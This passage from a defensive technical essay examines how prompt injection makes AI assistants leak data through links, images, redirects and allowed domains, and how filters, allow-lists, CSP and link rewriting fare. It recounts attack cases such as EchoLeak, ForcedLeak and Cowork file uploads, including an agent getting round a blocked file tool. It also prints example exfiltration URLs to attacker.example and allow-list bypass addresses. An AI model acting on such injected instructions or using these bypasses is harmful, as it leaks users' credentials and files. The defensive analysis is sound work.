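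Splitting the secret made individual requests look less suspicious. The first request contained recognisable sensitive data in 96.7% of runs when the model sent the secret whole, but in 26.3% when it sent the secret in four pieces. Part of this drop occurred because the split attack failed more often, producing a request in only about 77% of runs, compared with 99% for the whole secret. The results do not include how often all four pieces arrived, which is what an attacker would care about.

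The leakage figures for the split attack are also inconsistent. The paper reports a lower rate for the first three requests together (15.8%) than for the first request alone. This is impossible by its own definition, since any leak in the first request also counts towards the first three. A filter may still miss a fragment such as "48", but the 73% figure is weak evidence.

Lan and colleagues then compared defences, running each one 30 times against the version of the attack that put the instruction in the page's body and sent the secret whole.

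| Defence | Runs in which the model tried to send the secret | Runs in which a request got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| System prompt with a rule against following web content | 20 | 20 |
| Tags marking the page as untrusted | 30 | 30 |
| Both of these | 17 | 17 |
| Domain allow-list | 30 | 0 |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 25 | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 7 | 0 |
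| Filter for random-looking values | 0 | 0 |
| All of the above | 0 | 0 |

Instructions to the model helped somewhat, but more than half of the attacks still succeeded with both instructions in place. No data leaked under any of the checks on the request itself, though the test set-up made this easier for some of them. The attacker's domain was not on the allow-list, and the filter for suspicious addresses blocked any path containing the word "collect", which the attack's addresses contained.

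The results for the two content filters are harder to interpret. The filters run after the model has written a request, so they should not affect how often it tries to leak the secret. Yet the model made 30 attempts without any defence, seven with one filter and none with the other. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when such monitoring is active, but they do not explain how it could detect the monitoring. The filter that received no requests was never tested. The allow-list gives the clearest result, because the model tried to leak the secret in all 30 runs and the check stopped it each time.

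A test on one small local model can show that the mechanism works and that a check on the final answer would miss it, but not how often a commercial product would leak data. Lan and colleagues placed the secret directly in front of the model and gave it a minimal system prompt, which both helped the attacker. However, they used simple, undisguised instructions, which probably made the attack weaker than a real one.

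They argue that larger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better and use tools more reliably. Notion tells its customers the opposite, that smaller models are more likely to obey injected instructions. The evidence on recent models mostly supports Notion, since none of the 720 attempts on Claude Code succeeded. But Copilot Cowork leaked files in every trial with Opus 4.7, which is far more capable than qwen2.5:7b, so using a capable model does not guarantee protection.

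### Harms that need no outgoing link

Blocking every outgoing request would stop the attacker from receiving data, but the injected instructions would remain in the model's context and could lead it to do something else.

Injected instructions can still change the assistant's answer. An email could tell the assistant to report that the user's landlord has a new bank account, or to leave the bank's fraud warning out of the day's summary. The user could then send the rent to the attacker, even though no private data has leaked. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* acknowledges that even with the setting on, an instruction hidden in an uploaded file or a cached web page can still make ChatGPT give a wrong answer.

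If the agent has tools that can change data, injected instructions can also make it use those. Notion warns that connected tools may delete data. Copilot Cowork can edit calendar invitations and reorganise shared folders, and PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) points out that it could move a confidential file to a place where more people can open it, which exposes the file without any web address. An agent could also copy the login code into a shared document that the attacker can read. OpenAI therefore advises administrators who use Lockdown Mode to let ChatGPT write to an app only if they can confirm that an attacker would not see the result.

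Lan and colleagues propose, but did not build, a defence that would also cover some of these actions. The system would label everything that came from a web page, along with any tool call influenced by that material. It could then block the labelled call or ask the user, whether the call opened an address or wrote to a file. It would be hard to decide which calls the page had influenced, because a model reads the page and the user's request together. A cautious system might label everything the model does after opening a page.

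The instructions can also outlast the conversation. Many assistants have a memory, a set of notes that the application adds to later conversations. An attacker who gets a false note into it can influence answers long after the hostile email is gone. A skill file can have the same effect. Copilot Cowork loads skills automatically from the user's OneDrive folder, so anyone who can write to that folder can plant instructions for every later session.

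Lockdown Mode doesn't change ChatGPT's memory, and users can switch the mode off for a single chat. If an injection stored an instruction in memory while the mode was on, that instruction could take effect in a later chat where outbound requests work again.

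## What users lose when links are removed

Deleting every link doesn't prevent harms that need no outgoing request, and it makes the assistant less useful to everyone, including users who aren't under attack. The more links its answers contain, the more users lose. Amani, Lee and colleagues (2026), in *Characterizing Web Search by Conversational LLM Agents*, analysed 171,264 conversations donated by users of four chatbots. ChatGPT searched the web in about 6% of its turns and cited four addresses on average when it did. *Synthetic Sources?* (2026) put questions about politics, health and the environment to four AI search engines and counted an average of nine citations per answer, among answers that had any in the text. Research agents cite far more. Rao, Wong and Callison-Burch (2026), in *Detecting and Correcting Reference Hallucinations in Commercial LLMs and Deep Research Agents*, counted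 41 addresses per query from OpenAI's agent and 113 from Google's.

### Which links still work

A developer can delete the whole address, delete only the query, or show the full address as plain text that can't be clicked. The effect on users depends on what the link is for.

| Link | Whole address deleted | Query deleted | Address shown as plain text |
|---|---|---|---|
| Citation: `https://news.example/2026/port-strike` | Reader has to search for the article | Usually works | Works if copied |
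| Documentation: `https://docs.example/timeouts?version=4` | Reader has to find the page and version | May open the wrong version | Works if copied |
| Shop: `https://shop.example/boots?size=42` | Reader has to find the product | Opens the boots without the size | Works if copied |
| Map: `https://maps.example/?q=51.50,-0.12` | Location is lost | Opens a map without the location | Works if copied |
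| Signed download: `https://files.example/report.pdf?expires=1800&sig=8f3a` | User cannot get the file this way | Server refuses the request | Works if copied before it expires |
| Code: `get("https://api.example/orders?status=open")` | Code fails | Code runs but may fetch every order | Unaffected |

A user who loses a signed download link can't find a substitute with a search engine. The link's query contains a signature that the server calculated with a secret key and checks before sending the file. The link is also a secret, as the Copilot Cowork attack showed, so a filter that looks for secrets in addresses might block the link that the user asked for.

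The damage to code is the hardest to notice. If the filter deletes a whole address, the program fails and the user can see why, but if it deletes only a query string such as `?status=open`, the program may run without an error and give the wrong result. Exempting code blocks makes sense because the renderer displays them as plain text, so an address in one sends nothing until someone runs the code. The user still has to check where the address leads before running it.

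Browser makers ran into the problem with queries when they tried to stop advertisers from tracking people through links. *PURL* (Munir, Lee and colleagues, 2023) reports that one address often contains both tracking data and data that the site needs to work, so browsers deleted only parameters on a list of known trackers. Brave's list had 59 entries at the time, Safari's 24 and Firefox's 23. Such a list is useful against advertising companies because they use the same parameter names on many sites. It would not help against an attacker who runs the receiving server and can give the parameter any name.

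Of the ways to remove a link, showing its address as plain text preserves the most for the user. The user has to copy the address into a browser, which is a nuisance, especially on a phone, but can see the real destination instead of words like "Your invoice". An attacker's address can still contain stolen data, such as a login code, and a user who pastes that address into a browser sends the data to the attacker.

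### Few readers open the sources, but the sources are often wrong

Users arguably lose little when citations are deleted, because hardly anyone opens them. *Investigating Click Behaviors On Google Search Result Pages* (Chapekis, Lieb and colleagues, 2026) tracked the browsing of 900 US adults for a month in 2025. Only about 1% of visits to a results page with an AI summary led to a click on a source cited in the summary. The true figure may be somewhat higher, because the researchers collected the result pages in April, after the March searches, and recorded at most three sources for each summary.

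People click more when they have a reason to check. Ouyang and Narechania (2026), in *Analyzing the Presentation, Content, and Utilization of References*, asked 12 students to judge the accuracy of answers from nine assistants. The highest click rate, for ChatGPT, was about 12%, which is low for people asked to evaluate the answers. Even so, most satisfaction scores were above 4 out of 5.

Survey answers are more encouraging. In Reuters Institute's *Emerging uses of AI chatbots for news* (2026), 4% of all respondents in 27 markets said they always or often click through from a chatbot to the original news source. Only 9% used chatbots for news at all, so that is roughly half of those who could have clicked. Respondents may well overstate how often they do this. The Decoder reports from the same survey that 44% of the chatbot users who click do so to verify facts.

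Users have good reason to check the sources a model cites. Onweller, Lumer and colleagues (2026), in *Cited but Not Verified*, had 14 models write research reports, fetched the pages the models cited and used another model to judge whether each page supported the claim. Among the leading commercial models, more than 94% of the links worked, but only 39–77% of the citations passed the factual check. The judge failed citations it was uncertain about, so some of the failed citations may be sound. More searching made the citations worse. When the limit on tool calls rose from 2 to 150, GPT-5.4's score fell from 79% to 17% and Claude Opus 4.6's from 80% to 58%.

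Estimates of how many cited addresses are invented vary more. Rao and colleagues put the share at 3–13% for ten models and research agents, counting an address as invented if it was dead and had no copy in the Wayback Machine, an archive of old web pages. Amani and colleagues found a share of 1–2% in real conversations. The difference is plausible because Rao and colleagues tested demanding research questions on models that are now old. Under either estimate, a wrong citation today usually leads to a real page that doesn't support the claim, which readers can discover only by opening the page.

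A citation is a poor guide to whether an answer is accurate. In *Evaluating Commercial AI Chatbots as News Intermediaries* (2026), GPT-5 cited a source in 97.8% of its answers but came fifth of six models for accuracy, while Gemini 3 Pro cited sources least often and came third. If an interface removed the addresses but kept the citation numbers, answers would still look reliable, but readers couldn't follow the citations to check them.

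A service could check citations before it deletes them. Rao and colleagues built a tool, urlhealth, that lets a model test its links and replace the broken ones, which brought the share of confirmed dead links below 1% for three models. But the tool tests an address by sending a request to it, so if an injected instruction has put the login code into that address, the test sends the code to the attacker. A service that runs such a tool on model-written addresses needs to restrict where the tool can connect, as it would for a browsing agent. The tool also can't determine whether a working page supports the claim.

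### Warning about every unknown link

The obvious compromise is to keep links and ask the user to confirm before opening one the system doesn't recognise. ChatGPT does this with a dialog titled "Check this link is safe". It shows the address, warns that opening the link may share conversation data with another site, and lets the user copy or open it.

OpenAI objects to relying on a rigid list of trusted sites and warning users about the rest. People visit far more sites than such a list would cover, so they would often see false alarms. OpenAI expects this to train them to click through the warnings without thinking.

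Some arithmetic shows how quickly false alarms can pile up. The two rates here are assumed, not measured:

```
hostile links:                    1 in 100,000
links that trigger a warning:     1 in 5

warnings per 100,000 links:       100,000 / 5 = 20,000
hostile links among them:         1
```

Even if the system catches every hostile link, 19,999 of the 20,000 warnings are false alarms. Someone who opens one link a day would see about 73 warnings a year and encounter a hostile link once every 274 years, on average.

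The real rates could be very different. If attackers single out a particular company, one in 1,000 of the links its staff see might be hostile, and there would be 200 warnings per attack. The developer can't control how many links are hostile, but can change how many harmless ones trigger a warning. Reducing that share from 20% to 1% would cut the original 20,000 warnings to 1,000. OpenAI tries to lower it by recognising individual addresses that are already public.

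The closest evidence on how people respond to repeated warnings is the study of coding agents in which only 13.6% of testers refused a dangerous command. Anthropic hired the 1,053 testers through a research vendor and gave them coding work in an environment built for the study. They knew someone was evaluating them, but not what for. Partway through each session, the text of one ordinary permission prompt changed to the dangerous command. (Approving it did no harm, because only the displayed text was different.)

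The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This fits OpenAI's objection, although tiredness could explain some of the difference. Anthropic's usage data are also consistent with the objection, since Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts. But most of those prompts are probably harmless, so the high approval rate alone doesn't prove carelessness.

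Anthropic published the study to support making auto mode the default, and auto mode's classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers also had none of their own projects at risk, which may have made them less careful than at work. But people tend to take more care when they know they are being evaluated, so it is hard to tell whether the 13.6% is too high or too low.

People would probably catch fewer hostile links than hostile commands, so that number doesn't apply directly to links. A link warning appears after the user has chosen to open something, so the user already wants to continue. The danger is also harder to see. A developer can recognise a command that deletes files, but `?c=482913` looks like any other query, even before an attacker encodes it.

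Other differences suggest that warnings may work better for links. Most people open few links, so they may never see 50 warnings in a sitting, and they lose little by refusing a link if the assistant can suggest another source. A dialog that names the specific risk, as ChatGPT's does, may also get more attention than a routine request for permission. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents for approval, so they don't approve everything automatically, though many of those rejections presumably have nothing to do with safety. The study is strong evidence against constant warnings, but it doesn't show how well a rare, specific warning would work, and someone would have to test that with links.

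### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI built Lockdown Mode for users who have so much to lose that they would rather give up features than judge each warning. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it on 13 February for organisations on ChatGPT's enterprise, education and healthcare plans. On 4 June, OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and to small businesses that manage their own subscriptions.

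The mode takes away much more than links, according to OpenAI's help page:

- ChatGPT can browse only cached copies of web pages, so search results may be missing or out of date.
- It may not show images in ordinary answers, and it cannot fetch them from the web. Users can still upload and generate images.
- Deep Research and agent mode are unavailable.
- Code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace, cannot get access to the network.
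- ChatGPT cannot download files to analyse, though it can work on files that the user uploads.

On personal accounts, the mode also blocks live access and changes to connected services when either would conflict with its protections. In company-managed workspaces, administrators decide which apps remain available.

These restrictions would have stopped ShadowLeak, which needed both Deep Research and a live request to the attacker's server. The help page does not list ordinary text links among the things the mode removes, so a user can apparently still leak data by clicking one.

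OpenAI considers the mode unnecessary for most people and gives executives and security teams at prominent organisations as examples of its intended users. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, described the target group as people at higher risk because of who they are, what they work on or what data they handle. For someone who uses ChatGPT mainly to research current events, losing live browsing would be a major drawback.

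OpenAI does not guarantee that the mode will keep data from getting out, even for the intended users. The remaining risks it lists are apps that are still enabled, unforeseen combinations of features, and new techniques. The mode also doesn't change network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent, so a developer who turns the mode on in ChatGPT has to restrict Codex separately.

Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, welcomed the mode but concluded that if ChatGPT needs it, the default settings do not provide robust protection against a sufficiently determined attacker. OpenAI's announcement supports this inference. According to the announcement, the mode disables some features entirely because OpenAI cannot give strong guarantees for them, yet those features remain available to everyone not using the mode. This doesn't mean that data is easy to steal from an ordinary ChatGPT account. Writing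 on Embrace The Red, Rehberger called the current version of ChatGPT's link checks "a significant improvement" but warned that the problem is not solved.

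## Allow-lists of trusted domains

A domain allow-list is a list of the only domains that links, images or tools may contact, and a program refuses all others. This keeps links to the assistant owner's wiki, ticket system and leave form, which are of no use to an attacker but would be lost if the assistant deleted every link.

All the attacks that Lan and colleagues' allow-list stopped tried to send data to an unlisted domain. An attacker who knows about the list will look for a mistake in how URLs are matched against it, or for a listed domain that can pass the data on to them.

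### How the check works

Suppose the list contains `wiki.trusted.example` and the model writes a link to `https://WIKI.trusted.example./leave?year=2026`. The address is legitimate but oddly written, with capitals and a dot after the host. A sound check handles it like this:

1. Parse the address into scheme, host, path and query, with the same parser as the program that will send the request. Refuse it if parsing fails.
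2. Refuse any scheme other than `https`.
3. Normalise the host. Change capitals to lower case, remove the final dot, and convert any letters outside the basic Latin alphabet to the form that DNS uses. The result here is `wiki.trusted.example`.
4. Compare the whole host with each entry on the list.
5. Refuse the address if no entry matches.
6. If one does, pass on an address rebuilt from the parsed parts, not the model's original text.

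The check ignores the path and query, so `https://wiki.trusted.example/482913` passes even though it contains the login code. This is harmless only as long as nobody outside the company can read the wiki's log.

Most matching errors come from comparing text instead of the parsed host. Each of these rules looks reasonable and lets through an address that leads to the attacker:

| Faulty rule | Address that passes |
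|---|---|
| The address contains `trusted.example` | `https://attacker.example/482913?x=trusted.example` |
| The address starts with `https://trusted.example` | `https://trusted.example@attacker.example/482913` |
| The host ends with `trusted.example` | `https://nottrusted.example/482913` |
| The host matches the regular expression `wiki.trusted.example` | `https://wiki-trusted.example/482913` |

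In the second row, everything before the `@` is a user name, and the host comes after it. The check in the third row needs a dot before `trusted.example`, because without it anyone can register a longer name with the same ending and pass. In the fourth row, the unescaped dot in the regular expression matches any character.

Parsing the address first prevents these errors only if the filter and the browser parse it the same way. Browsers treat a backslash in a web address as a slash, so `https://attacker.example\@trusted.example/` takes them to attacker.example. Some programming libraries treat everything before the `@` as a user name and return trusted.example as the host. The same kind of mismatch let reference-style links past Copilot's filter.

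A wildcard entry can work correctly and still allow too many domains. In a CSP, `https://*.trusted.example` matches every subdomain but not trusted.example itself, according to Report URI, a CSP monitoring service. That is fine if one organisation controls all the subdomains. But if the entry is `*.hosting.example` and the hosting company gives each customer a subdomain, an attacker can sign up as a customer and receive stolen data at an allowed address.

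### Where to enforce the list

A developer can apply the list in the renderer, in the browser or on the network. Each place covers different requests.

| Place | Requests it can stop | Requests it cannot stop |
|---|---|---|
| Renderer | Images and clickable links in its own window | Previews in other apps; an agent's own requests |
| Browser, through a CSP | Images and other resources that the page loads | Clicks on ordinary links; requests from servers |
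| Network of the machine that runs the agent | Connections from that machine, including those from code | Requests from the user's browser or another company's servers |

The renderer is the only one of these that can remove a bad link before the user clicks it, but it has to recognise everything that can cause a request. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes a Copilot preview that removed `<img>` tags from HTML but still loaded an outside image when Rehberger made it the page background in a style sheet. Microsoft tracks the flaw as CVE-2026-24299.

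A CSP doesn't have this weakness, because the browser applies it to the request, whether the request comes from a tag or a style sheet. A small policy for a chat page could look like this:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'self';
  img-src 'self' https://images.trusted.example;
  form-action 'self';
  base-uri 'none';
  frame-ancestors 'none'
```

The first rule lets the page load resources only from its own server. The second replaces that rule for images and adds one outside host. The last three must be set separately because `default-src` does not cover them. CentralCSP, a reference site about these policies, warns that `default-src 'self'` alone still allows data theft through forms, because injected HTML could include a form that submits to the attacker's server. `base-uri` stops injected HTML from changing where the page's relative addresses lead, and `frame-ancestors` controls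 which sites may embed the page.

None of these lines affects an ordinary link. According to CentralCSP, CSP's two navigation directives control where forms may submit and who may embed the page. If the model writes a link called "Your invoice" that leads to attacker.example, the user can click it and send the code even under the strictest policy. The policy also doesn't affect requests made from outside the page, such as Slack's previews.

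A CSP applies to the whole page, so its allow-list has to include domains that the model's output doesn't need. Copilot's long list of image sources was presumably for its own features, but an image in the model's output could load from any of them. A developer can avoid this by displaying the model's answer in a separate frame with a stricter policy.

A CSP can also help to detect attacks. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* defines a way for browsers to report blocked content to developers. If a browser reports that it blocked an image from an unknown domain in a chat window, an injection has probably reached the model's answer.

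An allow-list for an agent's own requests has to be enforced on the network of the machine that runs the agent. If the vendor hosts the agent, only the vendor can do this. A filter that doesn't decrypt HTTPS can usually read the hostname but not the path or query, which is enough to enforce a list of domains. The filter also has to restrict DNS lookups, because data can leave through them, as it could from ChatGPT's isolated environment.

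### Listed domains that pass requests on

Many websites have an address that forwards visitors elsewhere, for instance after a login or to count clicks. If trusted.example has one, an attacker can use it to get past the list:

```
request:  https://trusted.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/482913
reply:    302 Found
          Location: https://attacker.example/482913
```

An allow-list can fail when a trusted site redirects to an attacker's site. A check on the original address finds trusted.example and approves it, and then the browser or tool follows the redirect to the attacker. OpenAI gives this as one reason why a list of trusted sites was not enough for ChatGPT.

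A tool can guard against malicious redirects by running the full check on each new address instead of following redirects automatically. Browsers do something similar for images under a CSP, so the redirect above would fail if attacker.example was not on the list. But if a developer limits an entry to one folder, such as `https://cdn.example/logos/`, the browser ignores that limit after a redirect, according to the W3C standard. So if cdn.example also has a preview service outside that folder, a redirect from any other listed site can reach it.

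When a user clicks a link, the browser follows any redirect itself, so the application cannot check it. Before adding a site to the allow-list, the administrator has to find out whether it forwards visitors to arbitrary addresses, and leave it off if it does.

A program that follows a redirect can check the next address, but when a listed service fetches an outside address itself, the browser has nothing more to check. EchoLeak, SearchLeak and one of the three ReLeak attacks used such a service to get past Copilot's CSP. Aim Labs, the research team that found EchoLeak, published Simonovich's *ReLeak* (2026) on 3 December under its new name, Cato AI Labs.

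All three attacks began like EchoLeak, with a hostile email that Copilot retrieved, as Faisal (2026) explains in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*. The data left in a different way each time:

| What Copilot produced | How the data got out | Patched in 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| An image address containing the data | The browser loaded the image, and Bing fetched it from the attacker's server | 15 November (CVE-2026-124115) |
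| A Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file with a link containing the data | Microsoft's background processing accessed the file | 11 November (CVE-2026-124132) |
| Python code | The code sent the data from Copilot's sandbox to an outside server | 17 September (CVE-2026-78501) |

The Bing attack shows most clearly how a domain list can fail. SearchLeak had also used Bing, and Microsoft had fixed it by early June. Cato reported the ReLeak attacks between 29 July and 20 August, so Bing could evidently still relay requests after the June fix. Microsoft then took at least 87 days to fix the newer Bing attack.

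In the second attack, the chat page's CSP couldn't block the request because the victim's browser didn't send it. A renderer that checked every link in Copilot's answer would also have missed the malicious link, since it was inside a file. To stop the attack, the allow-list would have had to apply to the Microsoft service that processed the file.

The third attack exploited a flaw in how the allow-list was enforced, not in the list itself. Copilot's code was supposed to run without network access, which amounts to an empty allow-list, but the researchers got around this restriction. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, with a score of 8.6 out of 10.

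Microsoft made all three fixes on its own servers, so customers have nothing to install. Cato knows of no real attacks that used the flaws, according to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026).

### Listed domains where an attacker can collect the data

An attacker who can read what a listed domain receives does not need a relay. The simplest way to do this is to own the domain. In 2025 the security company Noma found that Salesforce, which makes software for managing customer data, still had a domain on its allow-list whose registration had expired.

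Noma used it in ForcedLeak, an attack on Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for AI agents. Companies can put a Salesforce form on their website where potential customers, or leads, enter their details. Anyone can fill it in, and Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection* reports that the description field holds 42,000 characters, which is plenty for hidden instructions. When an employee asked Agentforce about the new lead, the agent also followed the instructions in that field. It looked up leads' email addresses and wrote them into an image URL.

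Salesforce's CSP didn't stop the browser from loading that image because the policy still had a wildcard entry for the expired domain, as Willison points out in *ForcedLeak*. The entry was presumably safe when someone added it, and the browser matched the address against it correctly. Noma registered the domain, which was on sale for as little as $5 according to The Hacker News (2025), and the leads' data arrived in Noma's server logs. Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, quotes Noma as saying that without a way past the CSP, the theft "would have been impossible".

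Salesforce patched ForcedLeak by taking back the domain, correcting its CSP and enforcing a second list, called Trusted URLs, on its agents' output. Enforcement began on 8 September 2025, according to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*. A customer's own Salesforce addresses are allowed by default, and an administrator has to add any others.

According to PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk*, Agentforce's chat window replaces any address that isn't on the list with the text `[URL_REDACTED]`, including addresses inside HTML and style sheets. This is URL stripping with exceptions, so it still depends on recognising every way to write an address. If it misses an image's address, the corrected CSP should block the image. The redaction doesn't restrict an agent's tool calls, for which PromptArmor recommends other defences, such as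 human approval.

Administrators can also limit each entry to particular uses, such as links or images. PromptArmor advises them not to permit images from a domain they need only for links, to prevent automatic image requests to it. TechNadu notes that an entry applies throughout the customer's Salesforce organisation, so a domain added for an agent becomes available to other features.

An allow-list can include an unsafe domain from the start. Google's programming tool Antigravity came with a default list of sites that its browsing agent could open. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* (November 2025) reported that the list included Webhook.site, a legitimate service that developers use for testing. It gives anyone a web address and shows them every request sent to it, so an attacker could use it in place of the server in the mailbox example.

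PromptArmor hid instructions in one-point type in an online programming guide. When a user gave Antigravity the guide, Google's model Gemini collected passwords and pieces of code from the user's project. A setting blocked Gemini's file-reading tool from opening the file with the passwords, but Gemini then printed the file's contents with a terminal command. It wrote the passwords and code into a Webhook.site address and had the browsing agent open it.

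This attack required the browser tools to be on, but PromptArmor found three other ways to get data out that did not. PromptArmor published the attack without first reporting it to Google, because Google had already acknowledged such risks and warned users about them during setup. The site was still on the default list in March 2026, according to Agentpedia, an independent guide to coding agents. Users can remove it from the list.

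A listed service can also leak data through an ordinary account. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine that blocks connections to almost all domains. One exception is Anthropic's own programming interface, or API, where customers can upload files. In January 2026, two days after Cowork's release, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed how an attacker could use this exception:

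1. The user gives Cowork access to a folder of confidential property documents.
2. The user uploads a Word file found online, which contains hidden instructions and the attacker's API key, the password for an Anthropic account.
3. The user asks Cowork to analyse the folder.
4. Cowork uploads the largest file it can find to Anthropic, using the attacker's key.
5. The attacker opens the file in their own account.

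Cowork never prompted for approval. The demonstration used Claude Haiku, a smaller model, but Opus 4.5 leaked customer records the same way in a separate test with a different document.

The network filter had worked as designed, because the file went to Anthropic, an allowed domain. A domain list cannot distinguish the user's account from the attacker's. To do that, the filter would have to decrypt the request and reject any key except the user's own. Searching the URL for secrets would not have helped, because the stolen file was in the body of the request.

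Rehberger had reported the same weakness in Claude's chat product before Cowork existed, and Anthropic had acknowledged but not fixed it. TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* reported that, after PromptArmor's demonstration, Anthropic was updating Cowork's virtual machine to restrict file access. PromptArmor's page still describes the flaw as unresolved.

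### Which domains are safe to list

A domain is safe to list only if outsiders can neither read the requests it receives nor make it send requests they choose. A good reputation isn't enough, since Bing and Anthropic's API belong to well-known companies and both delivered data to an attacker.

This rule excludes more sites than an administrator might expect. Almost any large platform lets strangers open accounts, and many build previews of outside pages. Salesforce's guide, *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)*, uses `https://docs.google.com` as its sample entry. This suits a company that keeps its documents there, but Google serves its online forms from the same host, and anyone can create a form and read the answers submitted to it. An administrator who needs the entry should probably allow links but not images, and should not reuse it for an agent that can send requests by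 itself.

An internal site, such as a company wiki that fetches outside pictures for its users, could also relay a request as Bing did. The `'self'` in a CSP permits such a relay on the application's own server. A listed domain can also change hands, so the administrator needs to check regularly that the company still controls each one. Even if the main domain hasn't expired, a stranger can take over a subdomain that points to a cloud account the company has closed and someone else can claim.

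Allow-lists therefore work best for something like an internal company assistant that answers questions about holidays, expenses and open tickets. Its list might have three entries:

```
wiki.company.example
hr.company.example
tickets.company.example
```

The company owns all three domains, can find out what they fetch, and controls who reads their logs. Employees get working links, including the paths and queries that a filter might have deleted. They rarely need links to other domains, so blocking those links causes them little trouble.

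Such a company may not know at first which domains its staff need. Glean, which makes an assistant for searching company data, lets administrators flag untrusted addresses or replace them with a placeholder. Flagging is a sensible way to find domains missing from the allow-list during a trial, but it leaves the answer unchanged, so it doesn't stop data from leaving. The replacement setting removes only addresses that Glean rates as medium severity or higher.

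An allow-list can't keep up with what people read on the open web, where a research agent may need dozens of new domains for each question. In *Browser Allow List not available*, a post on Google's developer forum, an Antigravity user says they added "hundreds" of addresses by hand and asks for a way to add them in bulk. Probably no one checked each of those sites for redirects, preview services and expired registrations. Limiting the list to popular sites would make it shorter but not much safer, because attackers can often open accounts on them.

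## Rewriting links to go through a redirect page or image proxy

An assistant that links to the whole web can't work from a list of domains, but its developer can still control what happens when a browser requests a link. Link rewriting replaces each address in the model's answer with one on the application's own server and puts the original address inside it:

```
model writes:   https://attacker.example/logo.png?c=482913

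page contains:  https://go.trusted.example/?to=
                https%3A%2F%2Fattacker.example%2Flogo.png%3Fc%3D482913
```

(The second address is a single line in practice. `%3A`, `%2F` and the like stand for punctuation. Without them, an `&` in the original address would look like the start of another parameter for go.trusted.example, and some legitimate links would lose their endings.)

When the browser requests the new address, the intermediary at go.trusted.example can forward the request, show a warning, refuse, or serve a copy of the content.

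Rewriting links doesn't stop the theft by itself, because an intermediary that forwards the full address also forwards the secret in it. The request may come from the intermediary instead of the user's computer, but it is still for `/logo.png?c=482913`. In the table below, 203.0.113.7 is the user's computer and 198.51.100.20 is the intermediary.

| Design | When the code reaches the attacker | Line in the attacker's log |
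|---|---|---|
| Plain redirect | The user clicks | `203.0.113.7 "GET /logo.png?c=482913"` |
| Check at the click | The user clicks, and the address isn't known to be malicious | `203.0.113.7 "GET /logo.png?c=482913"` |
| Warning page | The user clicks and confirms | `203.0.113.7 "GET /logo.png?c=482913"` |
| Image proxy that signs whatever the model writes | The answer appears | `198.51.100.20 "GET /logo.png?c=482913"` |
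| Copy stored before the conversation | Never | None |

### Plain redirects

The simplest intermediary redirects the browser to whatever address is in the `to` parameter. This gives the operator a record of clicks and a way to block a domain after an attack is discovered, even for links in old answers. But the record contains the full addresses, so a second copy of the login code is now in a log that the company's own staff can read.

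Tenable's *The Trifecta* (2025) describes attacks on Google's Gemini, which at the time sent the links in its answers through a google.com address. In one attack, a malicious website planted instructions in the victim's search history, and Gemini then wrote a link containing the user's saved information, which a click would have sent to the attacker. Another attack made Gemini's browsing tool request the attacker's address directly, so the answer contained no link to rewrite. A plain instruction to do this failed, but the attack worked when the researchers imitated the format of Gemini's internal tool calls, which they had seen in its "Show thinking" panel. Google has fixed both flaws.

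A carelessly built redirect service can also create a new weakness. If go.trusted.example forwards visitors to any address, it is an open redirect, and anyone can write a link that goes through it. A fraudster can send out links that begin with the company's name, and another application that allows links to the company's domain may approve one that leads to attacker.example.

The usual fix is for the application to sign each link it rewrites and for the redirect service to refuse links without a valid signature. An attacker can still open an account, get the assistant to write a link to attacker.example, and copy the signed result. Such copies are less useful if signatures expire or work only for the account that received the answer.

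### Checks when the user clicks

Microsoft's Safe Links, a service for business customers, rewrites links in email and checks them when someone clicks:

1. An email arrives, and the service replaces each link with an address on a Microsoft domain such as `nam01.safelinks.protection.outlook.com`. A user who hovers over the link still sees the original.
2. The user clicks, and the service compares the original address with a list of known malicious ones.
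3. If the address is on the list, the user gets a warning page. Otherwise, the browser opens the site.

Safe Links leaves links in Teams and Office documents unchanged but checks them when a user clicks. Microsoft extended these checks to Copilot Chat, which Gandhi announced in May 2025 in *SafeLinks Protection for Links Generated by M365 Copilot Chat and Office Apps*. Customers without Safe Links get a simpler check of the address's reputation. In the same update, Copilot Chat stopped redacting links that appeared in the sources for its answer.

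Checking a link when the user clicks it helps against phishing, where an attacker may link to a harmless page and turn it into a fake login form after the email has passed the filters. It helps much less against data theft, because the harmful part is the code in the address, which is there from the start, and the page can stay empty. The check would catch attacker.example only if somebody had already reported it, and an attacker can register a new domain for a few dollars.

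Google's Safe Browsing check for Gemini has the same limit, though it happens before the user clicks. *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (Google, 2025) shows an email summary in which Gemini replaced an unsafe address with "suspicious link removed".

The developer also has to decide what happens when a link can't be checked. If Safe Links can't finish a scan in an Office app, its protection doesn't apply, although the desktop versions warn the user first. Some apps send the user straight to the clicked link if they can't read the organisation's Safe Links settings. Letting links through is defensible for an anti-phishing service, since blocking them would break every link during an outage. An intermediary meant to prevent data theft should block the request instead.

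Two link rewriters can also interfere with each other. Microsoft warns that Safe Links may be unable to process a link that another service has already wrapped. A company that rewrites links in its assistant's answers should therefore test what happens when those answers are emailed.

The most serious trap is the scanner. Safe Links "detonates" addresses without a valid reputation in the background, which generally means opening them in an isolated environment to see what they do. This is a good way to find malware. But if a scanner opens the complete address from the mailbox example, it makes the leaking request itself:

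```
198.51.100.20  "GET /logo.png?c=482913"  404
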